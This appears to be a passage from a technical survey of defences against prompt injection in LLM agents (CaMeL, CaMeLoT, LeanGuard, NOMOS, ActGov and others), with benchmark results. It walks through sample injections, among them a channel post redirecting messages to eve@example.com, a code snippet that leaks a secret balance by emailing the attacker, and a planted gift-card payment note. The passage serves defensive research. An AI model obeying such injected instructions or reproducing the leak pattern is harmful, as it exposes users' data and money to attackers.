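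Xie, Kersting and Neider (2022), in *Neuro-Symbolic Verification of Deep Neural Networks*, allow the specification itself to contain a neural network. This lets engineers state requirements such as "the car stops whenever there is a pedestrian on the road", even though nobody can define a pedestrian in pixels. A separately trained specification network supplies the definition:

for every image x: specification network reports a pedestrian in x ⟹ controller stops on x

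According to Manginas and colleagues, the tool translates the networks and the property into one logical problem and passes it to Marabou, an exact solver. Exact solving is slow, and in their tests Marabou took 314 seconds per image to verify a small digit classifier, several orders of magnitude longer than their interval method.

Engineers need the specification network because the controller has no formal specification for pedestrians. The deeper difficulty is that the specification network has none either, so proving it correct would take another definition of a pedestrian, which would raise the same problem. If the network classifies red lights as pedestrians, a successful proof shows that the car stops at red lights. A counterexample is also ambiguous, since the controller may be right to drive on when the specification network wrongly detects a pedestrian.

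Such a proof can still be useful. With it, the controller can fail to stop for a pedestrian only when the specification network misses that pedestrian, so the controller's failure rate is at most the specification network's miss rate. Measuring that miss rate takes labelled pictures of pedestrians, and engineers could test the controller directly on the same pictures. The proof therefore saves testing mainly when they check several controllers, or many versions of one, against the same specification network.

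## CaMeL: plans written as programs and data labelled by origin

A language-model agent is a program in which a language model calls tools, for example to read email or send money. The tool calls are its discrete interface, and its perception is the model's interpretation of the text it reads. Perception errors in the systems above were accidental, but an agent that reads email also has to handle errors that people cause on purpose.

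The usual attack is prompt injection, in which someone hides instructions in text that the agent will read, and the model follows them as if they came from the user. Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, gives the example of an email that tells an assistant to delete all of the user's emails. *SPA* (2026) explains that the attack works because instructions and data reach the model through the same natural-language channel. Detectors can recognize many such texts, but Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, considers even a 99 percent detection rate useless because attackers will look for the 1 percent that gets through.

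### A program written before anything is read

Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues at Google DeepMind introduced CaMeL in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). It divides the agent's work among three components:

- The privileged model sees only the user's request. It writes a program in a restricted version of Python that contains all the tool calls the task needs.
- The quarantined model extracts values, such as a date or an address, from untrusted text. It has no tools.
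- The interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program and calls the tools.

Willison proposed the split between two models in 2023. Debenedetti and colleagues pointed out that an attacker can still influence the values that the quarantined model returns. They therefore made the interpreter label every value with its sources (its provenance) and its permitted readers. A value computed from other values inherits their labels.

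Before each tool call, the interpreter runs that tool's policy, a short Python function that checks the arguments and their labels and returns "allow" or "deny". The policy for changing a bank password, for instance, allows the call only if the new password comes from a trusted source. Reader labels record who may read a piece of data, so if only the invitees may read a calendar entry, a policy can block an email that would send it to anyone else.

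### One message to Bob

Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, use this program as an example:

```
messages = read_channel_messages("general")
email = query_ai_assistant(f"Extract Bob's email from: {messages}", EmailAddress)
send_direct_message(email, "Meeting at 3pm")
```

Suppose an attacker, Eve, has posted in the channel that all messages should go to eve@example.com.

| Line | What the interpreter does | Label on the result | What Eve's post can change |
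|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | reads the channel and stores the posts | untrusted | the stored posts |
| 2 | gives the posts to the quarantined model and stores the address it returns | untrusted | the address |
| 3 | checks the policy for direct messages before sending | – | the recipient, if the policy allows the call |

Eve's post can't add a step to the program, because the privileged model wrote the program before any of it ran and never receives the posts, and the quarantined model has no tools. Even if the quarantined model follows an instruction in the post to forward the whole channel, it can only return a value, and the program accepts only an email address. But Eve can still redirect the message, because eve@example.com is a valid address, just as "open" is a valid report even when the door is closed.

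A provenance rule prevents this by allowing direct messages only to recipients from a trusted source. The address in line 2 inherits the untrusted label of the posts, so the interpreter blocks line 3. The interpreter checks the label and not the address itself, so the rule works even against attacks that nobody anticipated. For the same reason, it blocks the message even if the quarantined model found Bob's real address, unless the user approves it.

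### What CaMeL guarantees

CaMeL is designed to guarantee that every tool call that runs is a call in the program and has passed the policy that applies to it, given the labels the interpreter recorded. Neither property depends on how well the quarantined model reads, so both should hold even if an attacker controls all of its answers.

Both depend on other premises, however. The interpreter must be the only route to the tools (complete mediation), and it must track the labels correctly. The user's request must also be trustworthy, and Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, object that phishing can get an attacker's text into the request. According to *SPA*, tool descriptions usually go into the planner's context, so a malicious description can also mislead the planner before any tool runs.

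The guarantee about steps is also weak if the program is very general. In one benchmark task, the user asks the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) ran CaMeL on this task without policies. The privileged model sometimes wrote a program with a branch for each tool, so the text in the file determined which tools were called, and two attacks succeeded.

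CaMeL does not guarantee that a value is correct. If the policy trusts the company's address book and Bob's entry is out of date or has been tampered with, the message goes to the wrong person even though every check passes. In a related benchmark case, the user asks the agent to pay whatever a document says, but an attacker has replaced the document. Debenedetti and colleagues exclude this case from their threat model. Garby and colleagues consider it a limit of all defenses based on information flow, because the user asked for the document to determine the payment.

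CaMeL also doesn't check the text it shows to the user. Tallam and Miller describe a PDF with a hidden instruction to forward the file to an outside address. If the agent repeats that instruction in a summary, the user might follow it.

### Leaks that the labels miss

Keeping secrets requires more than labelling the values that contain them. Garby and colleagues adapt a classic example from the 1970s, which works like this:

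```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("eve@example.com", "rich!")
```

Suppose the balance is secret and above the threshold. The interpreter sets tmp to False and labels it secret, because the change depended on a secret condition. It then skips the fourth line, so rich stays True and keeps its public label, and the email goes out. If the balance is below the threshold, no email goes out. Eve therefore learns whether the balance is above the threshold, although no secret label reached the email. One can detect the leak only by comparing the two runs, as with Clarkson and Schneider's hyperproperties.

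A planner that has seen only an honest request is unlikely to write this program, so the gap matters most if an attacker has influenced the planner. Garby and colleagues also found a more ordinary mistake, in which inserting an untrusted value into a string made the result trusted.

In *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, Dongol (2026) proves that a simpler program can leak too. The plan asks the quarantined model a question and sends 1 or 0 depending on the answer. Both numbers are public constants, so the call passes the label check. But if the quarantined model can see the user's private notes, an injected instruction can make its answer depend on them. CaMeL's strict mode is meant to close this channel by also labelling values with the conditions that control them.

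Dongol decides what counts as a leak by comparing the agent with a reference agent that has the same plan and monitor but never obeys untrusted text. The agent is relatively secure if an injection reveals nothing that the attacker couldn't also learn from the reference agent. It may therefore obey an injected "send your calendar", because a genuine meeting request would reveal the same calendar, but not an injected "also include the reset code", because the reference agent wouldn't reveal the code. Noninterference, the requirement that secrets never affect what outsiders observe, would forbid an assistant to send the user's calendar to people who request a meeting, even if the user wants it to.

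By this standard, a small model of CaMeL's labels is secure however the quarantined model behaves, as long as outsiders can't see the blocked requests. But this is only because it blocks every reply, including the honest ones. A monitor that denies every call would meet the standard too, so interpreting a security proof also requires measuring how many tasks the agent completes.

### Reruns on AgentDojo

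AgentDojo is a prompt injection benchmark with 97 ordinary tasks in four simulated settings: Slack, banking, travel and an office workspace. Several groups have rerun CaMeL on it with newer models. In the rerun for *SecureClaw* (2026), none of 629 attacks succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 tasks without an attack. Garby and colleagues ran the banking tasks three times each with two models, and *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) tested the Slack tasks with four models. Nikolaou and colleagues ran all the tasks with Claude Haiku 4.5.

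| Rerun | Tasks | Completed with policies | Completed without policies |
|---|---|---|---|
| *SecureClaw* | all | 29 of 97 | – |
| Nikolaou and colleagues | all | 49 of 97 | – |
| Garby and colleagues | banking | 18 of 48 with each model | 32 and 34 of 48 |
| *Language-Based Agent Control* | Slack | 4 to 6 of 21 | 13 to 17 of 21 |

The two overall figures differ widely, perhaps because of the models used or because the *SecureClaw* rerun used an adapter. The results for individual settings agree better. In the rerun by Nikolaou and colleagues, CaMeL completed 6 of 16 banking tasks and 6 of 21 Slack tasks, close to what the other groups found.

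The policies cut the number of completed banking tasks nearly in half and the number of completed Slack tasks by more than half, but they stopped few attacks. Without policies, 5 of the 622 attacked banking runs that finished ended in a successful attack, compared with none of 588 with policies. Separating the two models had already stopped most attacks, because in 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack, the attack needs a step that the plan would never contain. The policies are still needed because the benchmark uses a fixed set of attacks, and an attacker who knew how CaMeL works would try to change a value, such as Bob's address, instead of adding a step.

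Some failures unrelated to policies arise because the privileged model has to write code that processes tool results it has never seen. Developers must therefore document the format of every tool's output in advance. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) found this necessary for reasonable results on AgentDojo and a second benchmark.

Garby and colleagues also built their own agent, which enforces some of CaMeL's policies but fails fewer tasks because of them. With the model MiMo-v2.5, it completed 26 of 48 banking runs, compared with 18 for CaMeL with policies and 34 for CaMeL without them. The number rose to 31 when they let the plan endorse certain untrusted values, which means declaring, before the planner has read anything untrusted, that a trusted step may use them. With endorsement, attacks succeeded in 2 of 1,296 runs across three models, both times in a task that involved making a payment based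 on a document the attacker had replaced. Garby and colleagues also give a machine-checked proof that endorsing a value cannot leak secrets, apart from what an observer can infer from whether the program finishes. A planner that endorses too much can still let an attacker choose the recipient of a payment.

### Checking the whole plan in advance

CaMeL checks each call at the moment it is due. If the last step breaks a policy, the agent has already spent time and money on the earlier ones, and may have changed things that are hard to undo. Policies for single calls also can't naturally express requirements such as "every ticket that the agent opens must eventually be closed." Nikolaou and colleagues built CaMeLoT, an extension of CaMeL, to check the plan before any tool runs:

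1. It parses the program into tool calls, assignments, branches and loops.
2. It builds a finite-state model with a state for each point in the program. Labels record which tools the plan has called so far and which arguments are tainted, meaning that they may come from an untrusted source.
3. The model checker nuXmv checks rules written in CTL, a temporal logic that can also distinguish between "on every path" and "on some path".
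4. If a rule fails, CaMeLoT turns the counterexample into a request to the privileged model to repair the plan, then checks the new version. It gives up after a fixed number of attempts.

The model of the Bob program has five states: a start, one for each line, and an end. The rule is:

on every path, always (the plan sends a direct message → the recipient is trusted)

In the counterexample, the plan reads the channel, extracts the address and reaches the third line with a tainted recipient. CaMeLoT finds this counterexample without reading the channel or calling the quarantined model. If a plan passes CaMeLoT's check, CaMeL still applies its usual checks while the plan runs.

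Two rules for an agent that handles security alerts show the difference between safety and liveness:

- always (the plan isolates a computer → it has already requested approval)
- always (the plan opens a ticket → it eventually resolves or escalates the ticket)

The approval rule is a safety property, so a counterexample can stop at the step that isolates the computer. The ticket rule is a liveness property, which a run-time monitor can't check, but CaMeLoT can because it has the entire plan. A path that ends with the ticket still open is a counterexample.

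Both rules cover the calls in the plan, not their results. Nikolaou and colleagues describe the approval rule as "human approval before strong action", but the formula requires only that the plan request approval. Their example of a safe plan requests approval and then isolates the computer without checking the answer, so it is safe only if the tool itself waits for approval. Likewise, the ticket may stay open if the tool that resolves it fails or if CaMeL blocks the call.

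### Why loops can cause false alarms

To keep the model finite, CaMeLoT ignores the conditions of loops and branches. The model may skip a loop or enter it, and after each pass it may continue or leave.

Suppose a plan confirms three named computers in a loop and then isolates them. The loop always runs three times, so the plan never isolates a computer before confirming it. But the model of the plan also contains a path that skips the loop and goes straight to isolation. The model checker reports this path as a violation and rejects a safe plan. The model also contains a path that never leaves the loop. Unless the checker excludes this path, it will report a violation of any rule that requires a step after the loop to eventually happen.

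These errors are cautious for rules about every path, because the model contains all the real paths along with some impossible ones. For rules that require only that some path exists, the check can accept a plan that breaks the rule. For example, given a request to check recent transactions and change the password if any look suspicious, CaMeLoT derives the rule that a password change must remain possible after the check. A plan that changes the password only under a condition that can never be true would pass, because the model ignores the condition.

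### What the tests of CaMeLoT found

Nikolaou and colleagues first translated CaMeL's AgentDojo policies into temporal rules. They could fully express 22 of 28. Most of the others depend on facts that nobody knows in advance, such as who will have access to a file. They then ran both systems on the 97 tasks without attacks and with repair of rule violations turned off:

| Result | Tasks |
|---|---|
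| both completed the task | 42 |
| both blocked the plan | 17 |
| both allowed the plan, but it didn't do the task | 22 |
| only CaMeLoT completed the task | 9 |
| only CaMeL completed the task | 7 |

In the 17 tasks that both blocked, CaMeLoT avoided running the plan up to the violation. The 9 tasks that only CaMeLoT completed add nothing in normal use, because CaMeL still checks every plan that CaMeLoT accepts. Without repair, the combined system would complete about 42 tasks, 7 fewer than CaMeL alone. Six of those 7 are probably false alarms, because they are office tasks, where CaMeLoT could only approximate the trust labels for 13 of 14 tool outputs. The experiment doesn't show how many of these tasks repair would recover.

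In another test, Nikolaou and colleagues wrote a safe plan for handling a security alert and seven unsafe variants, each breaking one rule. CaMeLoT rejected all seven, while a simplified version of CaMeL caught only the one with a tainted argument. The researchers chose rules that CaMeL can't express, so the result shows what CaMeLoT can check but not how often real agents break such rules.

CaMeLoT can also derive rules from the user's request. A language model fills in one of ten fixed forms, such as "b is allowed only after a", and ordinary code translates the form into CTL. All 182 formulas produced this way were valid, compared with 182 of 655 when a small model, GPT-4.1 nano, wrote CTL directly. But a valid formula can still express the wrong requirement. The extracted list of required actions exactly matched the correct one in 85 of the 97 tasks.

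### Using the plan to recover

When CaMeLoT rejects a plan, the agent has not acted yet, so the planner can start over. An agent whose call is blocked halfway through a task has to continue from where it is. *SOTERIA* (He, Desai and colleagues, 2026) uses the verified plan to guide the agent from there. The system is meant for agents that have to follow business procedures, and the paper does not test it against prompt injection.

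A Soteria plan is a graph of steps, with conditions that determine which step comes next. Dafny, an automated program verifier, checks three things before any tool runs: that every call meets its tool's preconditions, that the plan can't get stuck, and that every path follows the policy. For example, an airline may cancel a reservation only if the passenger hasn't flown any part of it:

for every call c that cancels a reservation, there is a call c′ that checks for flown flights, where c′ comes before c, c′ concerns the same reservation, and c′ returned "none flown"

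CaMeLoT's approval rule requires only a call, but this rule also requires the call to return a particular answer. Soteria can express it because its verification model records arguments and results. Soteria also handles liveness rules, such as requiring an agent to read a file back after writing it. It avoids CaMeLoT's false alarms about loops, but only because it rejects plans that contain cycles.

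CaMeL's interpreter runs the plan exactly as written, whereas in Soteria's usual mode a language model chooses each tool call and may depart from the plan. A monitor checks every proposed call against the same policy and blocks violations, even if Soteria could not fully verify the plan. After a call is blocked, the model gets the plan's remaining steps and can choose one that leads to the goal.

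He and colleagues tested Soteria with four language models on 207 tasks in airline service, retail service and work with files. They counted a task as successful only if the agent completed it without violating the policy. Averaged over all combinations of model and benchmark, Soteria succeeded in 46.9 percent of tasks, compared with 27.5 percent for the best competing method. With Claude Opus 4.6, success rose from 56 to 88 percent on airline tasks and from 46.5 to 90.4 percent on retail.

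Much of the gain comes from avoiding violations rather than completing more tasks. If tasks completed with a violation also count, the best competing methods average 40.4 percent and the gain shrinks to about 1.2-fold. On the file tasks, Claude Opus 4.6 completed 30.2 percent without safeguards and 18.6 percent with Soteria, but more than half of the completions without safeguards broke a rule.

It is less clear how much the verification itself contributes. He and colleagues added the components one at a time on the airline tasks:

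| Configuration | Success with GPT-5.4-mini | Success with Gemini 3 Flash |
|---|---|---|
| unverified plan | 44% | 32% |
| with verification | 46% | 32% |
| with verification and reusable sub-plans | 50% | 38% |
| with the monitor as well | 60% | 62% |

The monitor made the largest difference, but the experiment didn't include a monitor without a plan, so it can't separate the benefit of blocking violations from that of guided recovery. In the airline and retail tests, Soteria cost between 1.7 and 6.7 times as much per task as an unguarded agent, because it makes a new plan at each turn of the conversation. On the file tasks, which need only one plan, it was cheaper.

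### Who writes the policies

All three systems check actions against rules that someone has to write. The CaMeL paper lists the work of specifying and maintaining policies as a limitation. Willison is wary of any design that requires ordinary users to think about security policies, which he still finds hard to get right after two decades of work on application security. In a company, specialists would do this work, but Tallam and Miller expect the rules to become duplicated, inconsistent and impossible to review as a whole when each of hundreds of tools has its own Python function. They recommend a shared library of rules in a language designed for policies.

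When no rule fits, the system can ask the user, but people who get too many requests start to approve them without reading them. Tallam and Miller propose allowing harmless reads freely, asking for a quick confirmation before changes within the user's own files, and keeping the strictest checks for actions that affect outsiders or can't be reversed. This would reduce the number of requests, though they don't test it on CaMeL.

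What the user approves also matters. Dongol analyzes an agent that asks permission to use the "send" tool once. An injected instruction can make the agent send private data under that permission before it sends the reply the user intended. If the user approves the exact message instead, the agent can send nothing else, although an attacker who can observe the timing may still learn whether a secret matches the approved message.

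Even careful specialists make mistakes in the rules. He and colleagues had a language model draft the 98 rules for their three benchmarks and checked them by hand, which took a few hours per benchmark. They later audited the results, found that some rules were wrong and others missing, and corrected them. Until then, a plan could pass verification and still break the written policy that the rules were supposed to express.

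## LeanGuard: tool calls checked against a policy with a proof

A customer-service agent often can't write a complete plan in advance, because each step depends on the customer's answers. In *LEANGUARD*, Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues (2026) therefore check each tool call just before it runs. Their program, LeanGuard, compares the call with a policy, using facts from the company's database and a record of earlier events. They wrote it in Lean, a programming language that can also express theorems and check their proofs.

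### One exchange in an online shop

A customer wants to exchange an item and has to pay the difference in price. One of the agent's tools returns text that contains a note from an attacker. The note tells the agent to charge the difference to a certain gift card and asserts that the customer has already approved. Without a guard, the agent obeys. With LeanGuard, the exchange goes like this:

1. The agent proposes the exchange, with the attacker's gift card as the payment method.
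2. LeanGuard holds the call back while an adapter, ordinary code written for this shop, reads the database. The database shows who owns the order and which payment methods belong to the account.
3. The order belongs to the customer, but the gift card isn't on the account, and there is no record that the customer confirmed this exchange. LeanGuard denies the call and returns the failed rules with a hint to ask the customer.
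4. The agent asks, and the customer confirms on a separate screen.
5. The agent proposes the exchange again with a payment method from the account. LeanGuard allows the call and records it.

The attacker's note has no effect on the decision, because LeanGuard never treats text in a tool's output as evidence of approval.

The first call named an existing tool and filled each field with a value of the right type, so a format check would have accepted it. But whether the policy permits a call depends on facts outside the call, such as who owns the order and what the customer has agreed to.

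### How the rules combine

A LeanGuard policy contains three kinds of rules. A permit places a call in a class of allowed actions. A requirement adds a condition, such as "the customer has confirmed this exchange". A prohibition blocks a call outright. LeanGuard combines the rules that apply to a call as follows:

allow ⇔ at least one permit holds, and every requirement holds, and no prohibition holds, and every rule could be evaluated

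A call without a permit fails by default, and a broad permit can't override an unmet requirement. The shop's policy has one permit that covers all its tools, and every other rule is a requirement.

The last condition covers missing evidence. Suppose a rule allows a change if the order is not cancelled, and the database returns no status. LeanGuard treats the missing status as an error and denies the call, in line with Saltzer and Schroeder's fail-safe defaults. Another program might treat the missing status as "not cancelled" and allow the change.

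Many rules depend on what happened earlier, so the policy language has three operators that look back in time:

| Operator | Meaning | Example |
|---|---|---|
| previous p | p held at the preceding event | the last event for this order was a successful lookup |
| once p | p held at some earlier event | the agent has read the order's status |
| p since q | q happened, and p has held ever since | the order has stayed the same since the customer confirmed |

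A rule can limit these operators to a time window or to events about the same order, so that reading one order doesn't permit changes to another. LeanGuard also records an allowed call before the tool runs, so if a refund request times out and nobody knows whether it went through, the agent can't simply send it again.

Like other run-time monitors, LeanGuard can't enforce liveness properties, such as a rule that the agent must send every refund that the shop owes.

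### What the theorem proves

Sankar and colleagues defined the meaning of a policy both as the program that evaluates it and as a set of formulas in temporal logic. Their main theorem is that, for every policy and every history of any length, if the program returns "allow", the call satisfies the formulas. In the proof, they read the history from the newest event to the oldest, which turns the operators "once" and "since" into "eventually" and "until", so an existing Lean library for ordinary temporal logic can supply the definitions. Lean checks the proofs when someone builds the policy, so no call has to wait for a proof.

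The theorem rules out evaluator bugs that would allow a call the formal policy denies. We need three more premises, which the theorem doesn't establish, to conclude that the agent can't do anything the company forbids.

The first assumption is that the adapter correctly returns what is in the database. If it returned the wrong owner for an order, the ownership rule would allow the wrong person's request.

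The second is complete mediation. A tool that runs arbitrary shell commands would undermine it, because one allowed call could change almost anything. LeanGuard denies calls whose effects it can't determine. In one set of tests, it denied 5,792 such calls, almost half of which were shell commands.

The third premise is that the formal policy matches what the company wants. For their main test, Sankar and colleagues had a language model draft rules from three written policies, then corrected them by hand, which produced 45 rules for 43 tools in 583 lines of Lean. They formalized only the parts of the policies that a check on tool calls can enforce, and their proofs don't show whether a rule is wrong or missing.

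### From a conversation to a record of consent

The confirmation rule still depends on perception, because LeanGuard needs a record that the customer agreed, and customers express agreement in ordinary language. The record names the exact action, its arguments and the details displayed to the customer. It works only once, so approval of one exchange can't authorize another. The theorem covers whether a matching, unused record exists, but not whether the customer agreed. *Agenra* (2026), another system with a core verified in Lean, has the same limit. Its monitor checks that an approval exists and uses it up, but doesn't check whether the reviewer judged correctly.

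A screen with a "confirm" button would leave little to interpret. The experiments instead used a separate language-model call, which decided from the conversation whether the customer had agreed. It sometimes got this wrong, for example by creating an approval that left out the customer's payment limit. LeanGuard then allowed a call the customer had not agreed to, even though the call satisfied every rule.

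Even with a correct transcript, people can disagree about whether an agent followed the policy. The airline and retail policies in the test require an explicit "yes" before any change, but it is debatable whether one "yes" covers two changes that the agent announced together. Yu, Kim and Choi (2026), in *NOMOS*, measured how often an unguarded agent broke the airline's rules. They found that 66.3 percent of its changes were violations if each change needed its own confirmation, compared with 36.8 percent if one confirmation covered the whole batch.

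### Results in customer service

Sankar and colleagues tested five Qwen models, with 0.8 to 27 billion parameters, on 278 tasks from *τ²-Bench* (2025), which simulates customers of a shop, an airline and a phone company. Each model tried each task once without a guard, once with a guard that denied calls without explanation, and once with a guard that explained its denials.

| | No guard | Denial only | Denial with explanation |
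|---|---|---|---|
| Forbidden calls that changed data | at least 33 | 0 | 0 |
| Tasks completed | 72.7% | 68.9% | 70.9% |
| Runs that a language-model judge flagged | 9.7% | 5.6% | 6.5% |

The zeros follow from the design, because LeanGuard runs only the calls it has allowed. They show that the software works as intended, but they aren't independent evidence that the policy is right. The 33 calls occurred in 28 of 1,390 runs. The true number is probably higher, because runs without a guard had no confirmation screen and nobody could check them for missing consent. In the guarded runs, 338 of the 1,702 blocked calls were changes that the customer hadn't confirmed.

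With explanations, the overall drop in completed tasks was too small to distinguish from chance. Completion of the shop tasks fell from 73.9 to 66.0 percent, while the other two businesses gained slightly. One of the shop rules was stricter than the written policy and blocked 158 calls, which may account for part of the loss.

The judge still flagged some guarded runs because it also checked requirements with no formal rule, such as not transferring a customer to a human too early. Some flags were mistakes by the judge, which was one of the tested models. For instance, it flagged 18 roaming activations even though the phone company's data showed the customer was abroad.

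### Results under attack

The second test used *DecodingTrust-Agent Platform (DTap)* (2026), a collection of simulated applications with attacks on the agents that use them. Direct attacks put the malicious instruction in the request to the agent, and indirect attacks hide it in data the agent reads.

| | All seven domains, no guard | All seven domains, LeanGuard | Telecom, no guard | Telecom, LeanGuard |
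|---|---|---|---|---|
| Direct attacks that succeeded | 57.9% | 5.9% | 55.1% | 2.4% |
| Indirect attacks that succeeded | 22.3% | 3.8% | 13.0% | 1.2% |
| Ordinary tasks completed | 53.1% | 12.5% | 75.1% | 75.3% |

The agents were allowed to read the customer's own records and public data, but not to change anything. This restriction blocked most attacks, but it also blocked most ordinary tasks. In the travel, finance and legal domains, no direct attack succeeded and the agents completed no ordinary tasks. Telecom was the exception because its ordinary tasks rarely require changes.

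A single rule blocking all changes would probably have produced similar figures, so this test provides little evidence about LeanGuard's confirmation and ordering rules. A better test would give the agents permission to make the changes that ordinary tasks need, then measure how many attacks exploit that permission.

The 289 attacks that succeeded despite LeanGuard worked through text. LeanGuard allowed no call that changed data in any of them, and no call at all in 158. For example, the agent misstated the amount of a bill or asked for passport or card details under a false pretext. Among customer-service and travel attacks that needed only a reply, 30.2 percent succeeded with the guard and 41.0 percent without it. LeanGuard checks tool calls but not replies to the customer, so no rule about those calls can ensure that the replies are true.

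### Repairing a denied call

After a denial, the agent has to find another way to do the task. In the customer-service test, agents that received only a denial later completed 34 of 620 blocked actions, compared with 48 of 526 when they also received an explanation. These rates are low partly because many of the blocked actions should never go through. Some had already been done, and others broke a rule that no confirmation could override.

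Lean can also search for a repair without the language model. It tries up to 32 changes to the call's arguments and returns the first changed call that it can prove the policy allows. Of 1,613 denials, 252 were due to the arguments. Lean found a repair for 88 of these (35 percent), typically in about 2 milliseconds. In 64 cases the repair sent a refund to the original payment method, and in 18 it charged a flight change to a card instead of a travel certificate.

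The search ran on recorded conversations, so the agents never used these repairs. The proof shows only that the policy allows the new call. People wrote a separate condition that defines which edits preserve the customer's intent. A customer who asked for a refund to a gift card may not want it on the original card, so the customer should have to confirm a repair like this.

### Deriving rules from possible harms

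LeanGuard's theorem takes the policy as given. *Tether* (2026) describes a way to check the policy itself. A user states a property, such as "secret data never reaches the agent", and a language model tries to write a Lean proof that the policy guarantees this property for histories of any length. This can catch rules that fail to work together, but someone still has to think of the property to check.

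In *Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents*, Doshi, Hong and colleagues (2026) look for such properties with System-Theoretic Process Analysis, a method from aviation and other high-risk fields. The analysis starts with the people a system affects and what they could lose, then works back to the behavior that would cause the loss. Their example is an agent that resolves calendar conflicts. A user adds an appointment for treatment of a sexually transmitted disease, and the agent moves a work meeting to make room and reveals the reason in an email to a colleague.

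The analysis leads to two rules:

- An email may not contain event details that are private to people outside the event, unless the user approves.
- After every change to an event, the agent must email each participant.

The first rule treats all event details as private to non-attendees, so nobody has to recognize that this appointment is sensitive. Enforcing the rule is harder, because a language model that has read the whole calendar may mention any part of it. A cautious developer could block all emails once the agent has listed the events, or hide unrelated events from the agent. The second rule requires a future action, so all a guard could do is block every other call until the agent has sent the emails.

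Doshi and colleagues sort such rules by whether the system always blocks a flow, always requires it, allows it without asking, or allows it only after the user confirms. They also want every tool to declare what it can do, whether its data are confidential and how far to trust its output. If a tool labels private data as public, the guard will let the data out, so perception errors can also enter through these labels.

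They tested the idea on a model of the calendar agent in Alloy, a tool that searches all runs up to a fixed length. Alloy quickly found a leak in the model without rules but none once they added the rules, which still let the agent reschedule a meeting and notify the participants. They haven't yet built a guard that enforces the rules on a running agent.

### Compiling a written policy

Many companies already have written policies for their staff. NOMOS, the system by Yu and colleagues, turns such a policy into checks on tool calls. A language model reads each clause five times and proposes rules, using a fixed list of conditions such as "the user has confirmed". Ordinary code then removes defective proposals and keeps those that win a majority vote.

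One policy clause says that the agent must authenticate the customer at the start of the conversation. The model turned this into a rule that blocked every tool until the customer was authenticated, including the two tools that perform authentication, so no conversation could get past that point. NOMOS finds such deadlocks by checking whether a rule blocks the tools needed to satisfy it, and exempts those tools from the rule. Counting all mechanical defects of this kind, it repaired or rejected 29 of 79 proposals for the airline (37 percent) and 7 of 53 for the shop (13 percent). After merging duplicates, it kept 10 rules for the airline and 5 for the shop.

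Other rules work mechanically but have the wrong meaning. From "always check that the bill is overdue before sending a payment request", the model derived the opposite rule, which forbade payment requests while a bill was overdue. No check of the tools' names and arguments can reveal this error. Yu and colleagues found it by replaying old conversations, in which the rule would have blocked 47 of the 49 payment requests in successful runs.

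The evaluation checked the agents' changes against a separate set of handwritten rules. Violations fell from 66.3 to 2.6 percent of changes in the airline tasks and from 30.8 to 6.9 percent in the shop. Of the 40 remaining violations in the shop, 21 involved two clauses for which the compiler had produced no rule.

Handwritten rules can contain the same mistakes as compiled ones. The airline's policy says basic economy flights can't be modified but allows a change of cabin. The compiled rule and the handwritten one both blocked cabin changes too, so comparing them could not reveal the error. Yu and colleagues found it only when they had another language model review the refusals and checked its objections against the records.

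### Drafting rules with a solver

Zhang, Peng and colleagues (2026), in *ActGov*, also let a language model draft the rules, but use the solver Z3 to search for gaps. They first reduce each situation to a record r with a limited set of values, such as whether an argument came from an untrusted source. Z3 then looks for a record and a decision v that the policy allows but a safety requirement A forbids:

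there exist r and v such that Policy(r, v) and not A(r, v)

If Z3 finds such a case, the language model revises the rules. If Z3 finds none, the policy meets the requirement for every possible record, and a person reviews the policy before use.

The proof is about the records, though, and a language model fills in some of them while the agent works. If the model wrongly records that an attacker's address came from the user, the verified policy may approve the call.

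With DeepSeek-v4-pro as the agent, ActGov cut the attack success rate from 6.1 percent to zero on AgentDojo and from 8.6 to 0.7 percent on AgentDyn, a benchmark with less predictable tasks. When there were no attacks, the share of tasks the agent completed fell from 87.8 to 75.5 percent on AgentDojo and from 76.7 to 60.0 percent on AgentDyn.

These policies depended heavily on the tasks used to develop them. When Zhang and colleagues applied the AgentDojo policy to AgentDyn, no attack succeeded, but the agent completed only 10 percent of the ordinary tasks. Human review also seems to matter. Policies drafted without it, using half the training data and fewer rounds, let the agent complete 28 to 53 percent of AgentDyn tasks, depending on which model wrote them.

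### What enforcement costs

The cost depends on how closely legitimate work resembles an attack. Yu and colleagues wrote a one-page policy for each AgentDojo setting and compiled it with NOMOS:

| Setting | Successful attacks, no guard | Successful attacks, NOMOS | Tasks completed, no guard | Tasks completed, NOMOS |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Travel | 10.0% | 3.6% | 75.0% | 70.0% |
| Banking | 46.5% | 0.0% | 79.2% | 70.8% |
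| Workspace | 7.3% | 0.0% | 87.5% | 65.0% |
| Slack | 70.5% | 0.0% | 90.5% | 14.3% |

In Slack, a typical request is to summarize an article that a colleague posted. The agent has to open a link that the user never named, which is also what an attacker would want it to do. The rule that blocks the attack therefore blocks the legitimate request too, just as CaMeL's provenance rule blocked Bob's real address along with Eve's. Bank customers more often name the recipient themselves or pay someone they have paid before, and NOMOS allows both. In 8 of 288 attacked banking runs, it allowed a payment that the attacker had ordered because the recipient was already in the customer's payment history.

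A guard can also help an agent finish its task. In the airline tests, a forbidden cancellation leaves the database in the wrong state, so the agent fails the task. Blocking the call lets the agent try again. With NOMOS, the share of airline tasks completed in a single attempt rose from 39.2 to 47.6 percent, although a gain of that size could be due to chance. The share completed in all three of three attempts rose more clearly, from 23 to 37 percent. *Reason Less, Verify More* (Yu et al., 2026) also reports that a few short handwritten checks raised GPT-4o-mini's success on airline tasks from 29.6 to 42.0 percent.

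Sah, Sah and colleagues (2026), in *The Verifier Tax*, give a more pessimistic picture, but their verifier is a language model, not a proved program. It reviews each proposed action and can reject it up to three times in a row, after which the action runs anyway. They tested two small models on an earlier version of the airline and shop tasks. A success counts as safe if the agent broke no rule along the way:

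| Model and tasks | Success, no verifier | Success, verifier | Safe success, no verifier | Safe success, verifier |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-OSS-20B, airline | 22.7% | 23.3% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-OSS-20B, shop | 21.2% | 21.5% | 0.0% | 0.6% |
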